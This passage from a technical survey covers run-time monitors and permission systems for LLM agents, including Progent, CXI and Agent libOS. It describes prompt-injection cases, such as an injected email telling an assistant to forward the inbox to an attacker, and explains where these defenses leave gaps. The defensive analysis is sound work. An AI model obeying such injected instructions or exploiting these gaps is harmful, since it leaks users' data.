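| A tool added or changed during the run has permission to act | Tool called | Agent libOS |
| Data from an earlier session is trustworthy | Stored data read back | MemLineage |
| A retry is allowed and the budget can cover it | Tool called | Agent libOS |
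| The user approved exactly this call | Tool called | Agent libOS |
| An outside process had the intended effect | Result returned, if ever | Agent libOS |

Some facts are available earlier than the table suggests. If the user types the manager's address into the request, the plan contains it, and an analyser can check it before the run. A check during the run works on actual values, but by then the agent may have taken steps that nobody can undo.

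### What a monitor can enforce

A monitor is a mechanism that watches a program's steps and stops the program before a forbidden one. In 2000, Schneider, in *Enforceable Security Policies*, worked out which rules monitors can enforce. Write ok(s) if the rule permits the run s. A monitor can enforce the rule only if three conditions hold:

- The rule judges each run by itself, so a system obeys it exactly when ok(s) holds for every run s.
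- A violation is permanent. If ok(t) is false for an unfinished run t, it stays false however t continues.
- Every violation shows up after finitely many steps.

Rules that meet these conditions are safety properties, which state that something bad never happens. Schneider's example is a rule against sending messages after reading a file. The monitor needs only two states. It starts in "nothing read", moves to "file read" at the first read, and refuses every send from then on. According to Basin (2012), monitors can also enforce access rules that depend on a run's history.

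Costa and colleagues start from a labelled agent loop that is almost the same monitor, except that it moves to its second state only when it receives an untrusted result.

Monitors can't enforce every useful rule. The security agent that Nikolaou and colleagues describe must eventually resolve or escalate each ticket it opens. An unfinished run never breaks this rule, because the agent might still deal with the ticket later, and stopping the agent would only leave the ticket open. CaMeLoT can check the rule because it can follow every path through the whole plan to its end.

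Adding a deadline makes the rule a safety property, but it may not help much. If the agent has 20 steps to resolve the ticket, a monitor can prevent a violation by halting the agent before the twentieth step, but the ticket stays open. If the deadline is in seconds, the monitor can't prevent a violation this way because, as Schneider points out, stopping a program doesn't stop time.

### Why one run cannot settle noninterference

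Noninterference fails the first of Schneider's conditions. Consider two programs that email an outsider:

```
# Program A
if balance > threshold:
    send_email(outsider, "hello")
else:
    send_email(outsider, "hello")

# Program B
if balance > threshold:
    send_email(outsider, "hello")
```

Program A sends the same message whatever the balance is, so the outsider learns nothing about it. In Program B, the arrival of the message reveals that the balance is high.

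With a high balance, the two programs take exactly the same steps, so a monitor that observes only those steps has to treat them alike. If it allows the email, it misses the leak in B, and if it blocks the email, it stops a harmless run of A. Schneider concludes that monitors against information leaks enforce a rule that prevents leaks but also forbids some behavior that leaks nothing.

*Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) gives a general account of rules like this. It represents a system by the set T of all its possible runs. An ordinary property is a set P of permitted runs, and the system satisfies it if T ⊆ P. A hyperproperty is a set H of permitted systems, and the system satisfies it if T ∈ H. Noninterference is a hyperproperty because whether a run is acceptable depends on the system's other runs. A limit on the average response time over all runs is another, since one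 slow run doesn't determine whether the average is too high.

An analyser with the program's code can still check some hyperproperties by comparing runs. It makes two copies of the program, gives them the same public inputs but different secrets, and treats the pair as one larger program. The requirement that both copies produce the same public output is then an ordinary safety property of the pair. Program B fails this check when one copy has a high balance and the other a low one. Clarkson and Schneider prove that the method extends to k copies for any safety hyperproperty whose violations can each be shown with at most k runs.

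Running a second copy of the agent on an invented balance compares only one pair of balances, so it might find a leak but can't rule one out. The model's replies also vary, so the two runs may differ even if the balance had no influence.

Blocking runs can even create a leak. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that can output 0, 1 or the value of a secret bit. Both outputs are possible whatever the secret is, so the system satisfies a rule that the set of possible outputs must not depend on the secret. Blocking the runs that output a fixed 0 or 1 leaves only runs that output the secret. Blocking runs can never break a safety property, however. An agent's monitor must therefore be designed so that its refusals don't reveal confidential information, as they would if it refused to answer a supplier only when a confidential budget had shrunk.

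### Branches that a run skips

A sound monitor has to block some harmless work, and the amount depends partly on whether labels can change during the run. If every variable keeps the label it started with, the monitor can simply refuse any assignment to a public variable under a secret condition. Sabelfeld and Russo, in *From dynamic to static and back*, show for a simple language that such a monitor gives the same guarantee as the classic static analysis, which is noninterference apart from leaks through termination. The monitor also accepts more, because it ignores faulty lines that the run never reaches. They consider this flexibility particularly important for freshly generated code, which is what agents produce.

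The comparison changes when labels can change, as in CaMeL and LLMbda. Russo and Sabelfeld define a purely dynamic monitor as one that can't examine later instructions or the branch that the run skipped. They prove that no sound monitor of this kind accepts every program that a standard static analysis with changeable labels accepts. For example, LLMbda's no-sensitive-upgrade rule can stop a program for changing a variable that the program never uses again.

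A hybrid monitor avoids the result by statically analyzing the branch that the run skips. In the two-variable program that defeats CaMeL's interpreter, `tmp` stays public when the run skips the line that changes it. A hybrid monitor would analyze that line and mark `tmp` as secret whether or not the line runs. Russo and Sabelfeld prove that such monitors can be sound and accept more programs than the static analysis does.

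This approach works well for generated programs because they contain both branches, but it doesn't work well for the ordinary agent loop. In that loop, the skipped branch is the call that the model would have requested if an email had contained different text, and no code lists those calls. A monitor therefore has to treat every available call as one the email could have led to, which is why FIDES gives every new request the label of the whole conversation.

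FIDES offers a weaker guarantee for secrets. Costa and colleagues describe what dynamic taint tracking can enforce as a combination of explicit secrecy and safety properties. They consider this enough to stop most practical prompt injections, which seems fair for attacks that copy data out but not for those that leak it through the agent's choices.

### Progent's rules for tool calls

Progent enforces a safety property that is easy to state: the agent makes only the calls that its current rules allow. Each rule names a tool and restricts its arguments with exact values, wildcards or text patterns. If the user supplies the manager's address, the office assistant's rules could be:

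```
allow read_email(subject="Project X")
allow send_email(to="manager@company.example")
```

These rules block the injected command to write to the attacker but allow the summary, even though the assistant has read an outside email. The labelled loop has to block both. But the second rule doesn't restrict the body, so an injection could still make the assistant put private text from another email into the summary.

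Fixed rules don't work when the agent discovers its task along the way. Shi and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to do whatever Alice's weekly to-do email requires. A model writes the first rules from the request and proposes changes as results arrive:

1. The first rules allow only a search for Alice's email. It turns out to contain a request to summarise recent emails and post the summary to the user's Slack account.
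2. The model proposes rules for reading emails, looking up the account and posting to Slack. These allow new calls, so somebody has to approve them.
3. The lookup returns the account name "alice". The model proposes to allow posts only to that account, and Progent applies this change automatically.
4. One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the inbox to an attacker. If this fools the model into proposing a rule for `send_email`, the change again needs approval.

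When the rules change, Progent checks whether the new ones allow any call that the old ones didn't. It does this with an SMT solver, a program that determines whether a set of logical constraints has a solution, rather than with a model. The set of permitted calls therefore can't grow without approval.

Shi and colleagues found that 39.9% of attacks on AgentDojo succeeded without Progent and 1.0% with it. On ASB, another benchmark for agents, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Only 6% of the rule changes on AgentDojo needed approval.

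The guarantee doesn't cover where an argument came from. If an attacker could edit the profile that the Slack lookup returns, Progent would narrow the rule to the attacker's account without human approval. This adds no permission, since the previous rule allowed posts to any account, but the summary would go to the attacker. The refund attacks in the previous section exploited the same gap.

*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) adds that Progent doesn't address attacks on the agent's written answers, and that a poisoned tool result could cause an update to loosen the rules. The second point seems to concern an earlier version, because Progent now holds back updates that loosen the rules until somebody approves them. But it still applies if the operator sets Progent to approve every change automatically.

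### Context-to-execution integrity

CXI, published in July 2026, deals with the origin of arguments. Before an action with outside effects, ordinary code checks three things:

- Every important field, such as the recipient, has a value from a source that may set that field.
- If the call contains something that another program will interpret, such as a code patch or a database command, its exact effect has authorisation.
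- The call itself has authorisation to happen now, including when it is a retry or part of a schedule.

Suppose an outside email says that the manager has approved the summary and that the assistant should send it again if nobody replies by noon. The assistant may quote this text in the message body, because it is only data there. Trusted code could also extract a date from the email, check it and allow it in one specific date field. But the email can't supply the approval, choose the recipient or trigger a second message.

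CXI ties the three authorisations together with a manifest that records the exact action. If any part of the action changes after the check, it no longer matches the manifest and the call fails. A ledger also uses up the permission before the call runs, so a hijacked agent can't reuse it for another message.

The hardest part is establishing what influenced a field, since a model may pick a trusted tool name because of an untrusted email. In Santos-Grueiro's reference design, an open model generates each important field separately, from a prompt that contains only trusted information and values released for that field. A faster version keeps the full conversation but blocks the model's attention to untrusted passages while it writes the field. The simplest form of this version doesn't block text that the model wrote after reading those passages, so the passages may still influence the field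 indirectly. With a commercial model, the operator can't control attention and has to limit what each field's prompt contains.

In 400 coding tasks, Santos-Grueiro observed no unauthorised field, effect or call getting past the checks, and the agents safely completed 231 of the tasks. Of the other 169 attempts, 73 produced output the software couldn't parse, 61 proposed an effect that wasn't authorised, and 35 ran but didn't solve the task. The checks therefore caused at most 61 of the failures.

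In a separate test, models had to choose between an authorised and an unauthorised action, and chose the unauthorised one in 196 of 300 adversarial cases. None of these actions ran. The checks had more unauthorised actions to stop than they often do in AgentDojo, but a forced choice is weak evidence of how often a model would propose such an action in ordinary use.

Santos-Grueiro also tested versions with parts of the design removed. The full version rejected all 20 attack cases. A version that tracked only where arguments came from rejected 12, and one with permissions for fields but no ledger rejected 10. The cases target specific mechanisms, so the results don't measure how common each attack is, but they show that tracking the source of every argument isn't enough to control repeated or badly timed calls.

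Someone has to classify every field before this works. The policies for 24 operations cover 149 fields. The initial audit found problems such as missing rules for executable content and approvals based on ordinary text. Santos-Grueiro resolved the blocking problems before the final evaluation, but a team that writes its own policies would have to find the mistakes in them itself.

### Agents that change while they run

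Agent libOS (June 2026) is designed for agents that write new tools, start other agents and save their state. Its central rule is that a new tool gives an agent something else it can request but no additional permission to affect existing resources.

Before an operation, the runtime checks that the agent has permission for the specific resource, the operation is within the task's limits, any required approval exists and enough budget remains. All four conditions must hold, so neither approval nor unused budget can replace a missing permission. If data leaves the system, the runtime also compares the data's labels with what the recipient may receive.

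A tool that the agent writes during a run can reach the runtime only through one interface, which applies the same checks as for built-in tools. If the office assistant writes a function called `tidy_inbox` that tries to forward mail, the function can do so only if the assistant already had permission. For remote tools, Agent libOS keeps a digest of the registered description and compares it again just before each call. This catches a change to the registration, but the server's owner could change what the tool does without changing the description.

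As in MemLineage, labels stay attached to stored data, but permissions must be checked again when the agent restores saved state. If the operator withdraws a permission on Tuesday and the agent then restores its state from Monday, the permission must not come back, so Agent libOS compares the saved permissions with the current ones.

The runtime also handles the dropped connection to the mail server. It records what it is about to do, makes the call, and records the outcome. If it crashes before recording the outcome, it marks the outcome as unknown and doesn't repeat the call automatically. Some services keep receipts the runtime can look up. If there is no receipt, a person may have to ask the manager whether the email arrived.

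Zhang tested these checks on 33 scripted tasks. Agent libOS carried out 119 effects, none of them unauthorised. A wrapper that passed calls straight to the tools carried out 29 effects, of which 20 were unauthorised. A wrapper that asked for confirmation carried out 64 effects, of which 20 were unauthorised.

The wrappers were deliberately simple, so the tests don't show how Agent libOS compares with competing products. They also don't show that every part of Agent libOS is necessary. Removing the separation between agents' data allowed two unauthorised effects, and removing the limits on copied agents allowed one, but removing approval for individual operations allowed none. All 12 workflow runs with a real model were safe and completed their tasks, which is encouraging, but the sample is very small.

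### User approval as a check

Several of these designs ask the user for approval when their rules don't settle whether to allow an action. Approval is also a dynamic check, and its value depends on what the user sees and what the system does with the answer.

Suppose the user approves the assistant's draft summary for the manager, but another email arrives before the assistant sends it, and the model rewrites the summary. A system that stored only "yes" would send text that the user never read. For sensitive data, Agent libOS ties a one-time approval to the exact content, recipient and source versions, with a deadline, so the rewritten summary would need a new approval.

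Exact approvals interrupt the user more often. Costa and colleagues warn that confirmation prompts can lead to fatigue, with users clicking carelessly as Willison expected, and to attacks that trick the user directly. Letting one answer cover more, as with Agent libOS's "always allow" option or Prudentia's endorsement of a whole email, reduces interruptions, but the user then approves future calls without knowing what they will contain.

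Counting prompts doesn't show which approach is safer. Progent's figure of 6% is a share of rule changes, so it could mean one prompt a week or several an hour, depending on how much the agent does. Prudentia's lower number of approvals is easier to interpret, but one approval may cover many actions. A useful test would measure how often people notice a malicious request after approving many harmless ones.

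The content of the prompt probably matters too. "Allow `send_email`?" gives the user little information. Labels would let the system add that the address comes from an outside email and not from the company directory, which the user needs to know to spot this attack. Labels wouldn't help with a forged bill in a file the user trusts, because the user may have no more evidence than the agent does.

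### The code that every run-time check trusts

Schneider lists what a monitor needs to work. It must receive every relevant step, it must be able to stop the program, and the program must not be able to alter it. The first requirement is harder to meet than it looks, because a system may have many ways to send a message, some of them deep inside it. In the office assistant, `send_email` is the obvious way, but `create_event` may email an invitation to every guest, and `share_file` may send a notification with a comment from the agent. A rule that covers only `send_email` would miss both.

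CXI requires every route to an outside effect to pass through its checks, and rejects fields that nobody has classified. Its guarantee also depends on the policies, the code that validates released values, the records of influence and the machine it runs on. Agent libOS trusts its own runtime, the Python interpreter, the database, the operating system and the person who grants approvals. It also trusts each outside service to some extent. A tool server on the user's machine runs as an ordinary program with the user's access rights. The runtime checks the requests sent to it but not what it does with them.

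A rule that allows the version-control command `git` allows much more than it seems to, because Git's options and settings can start other programs or send code to another server. Agent libOS offers only specific Git operations and disables the settings that run other code. However, if the agent also has permission to use a general interpreter, it can start Git from there and avoid these restrictions.

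Checks after a run similarly depend on the log. In *From Agent Traces to Trust*, Wang, Zhang and colleagues (2026) reviewed 71 works relevant to recording and tracing what agents do, and found little reporting of logs that reveal tampering. Agent libOS doesn't provide this protection, since an administrator with database access can change its records.

Static analysis can help with the first of Schneider's requirements before the agent runs. An analyser can search a tool's source code for ways to reach the network without passing through the monitor, much as AgentFlow and ACaM search for dangerous paths. This search stops being useful if the tool can run arbitrary commands. The operating system then has to enforce the limits, for instance with a sandbox that blocks all network access except through the monitor.
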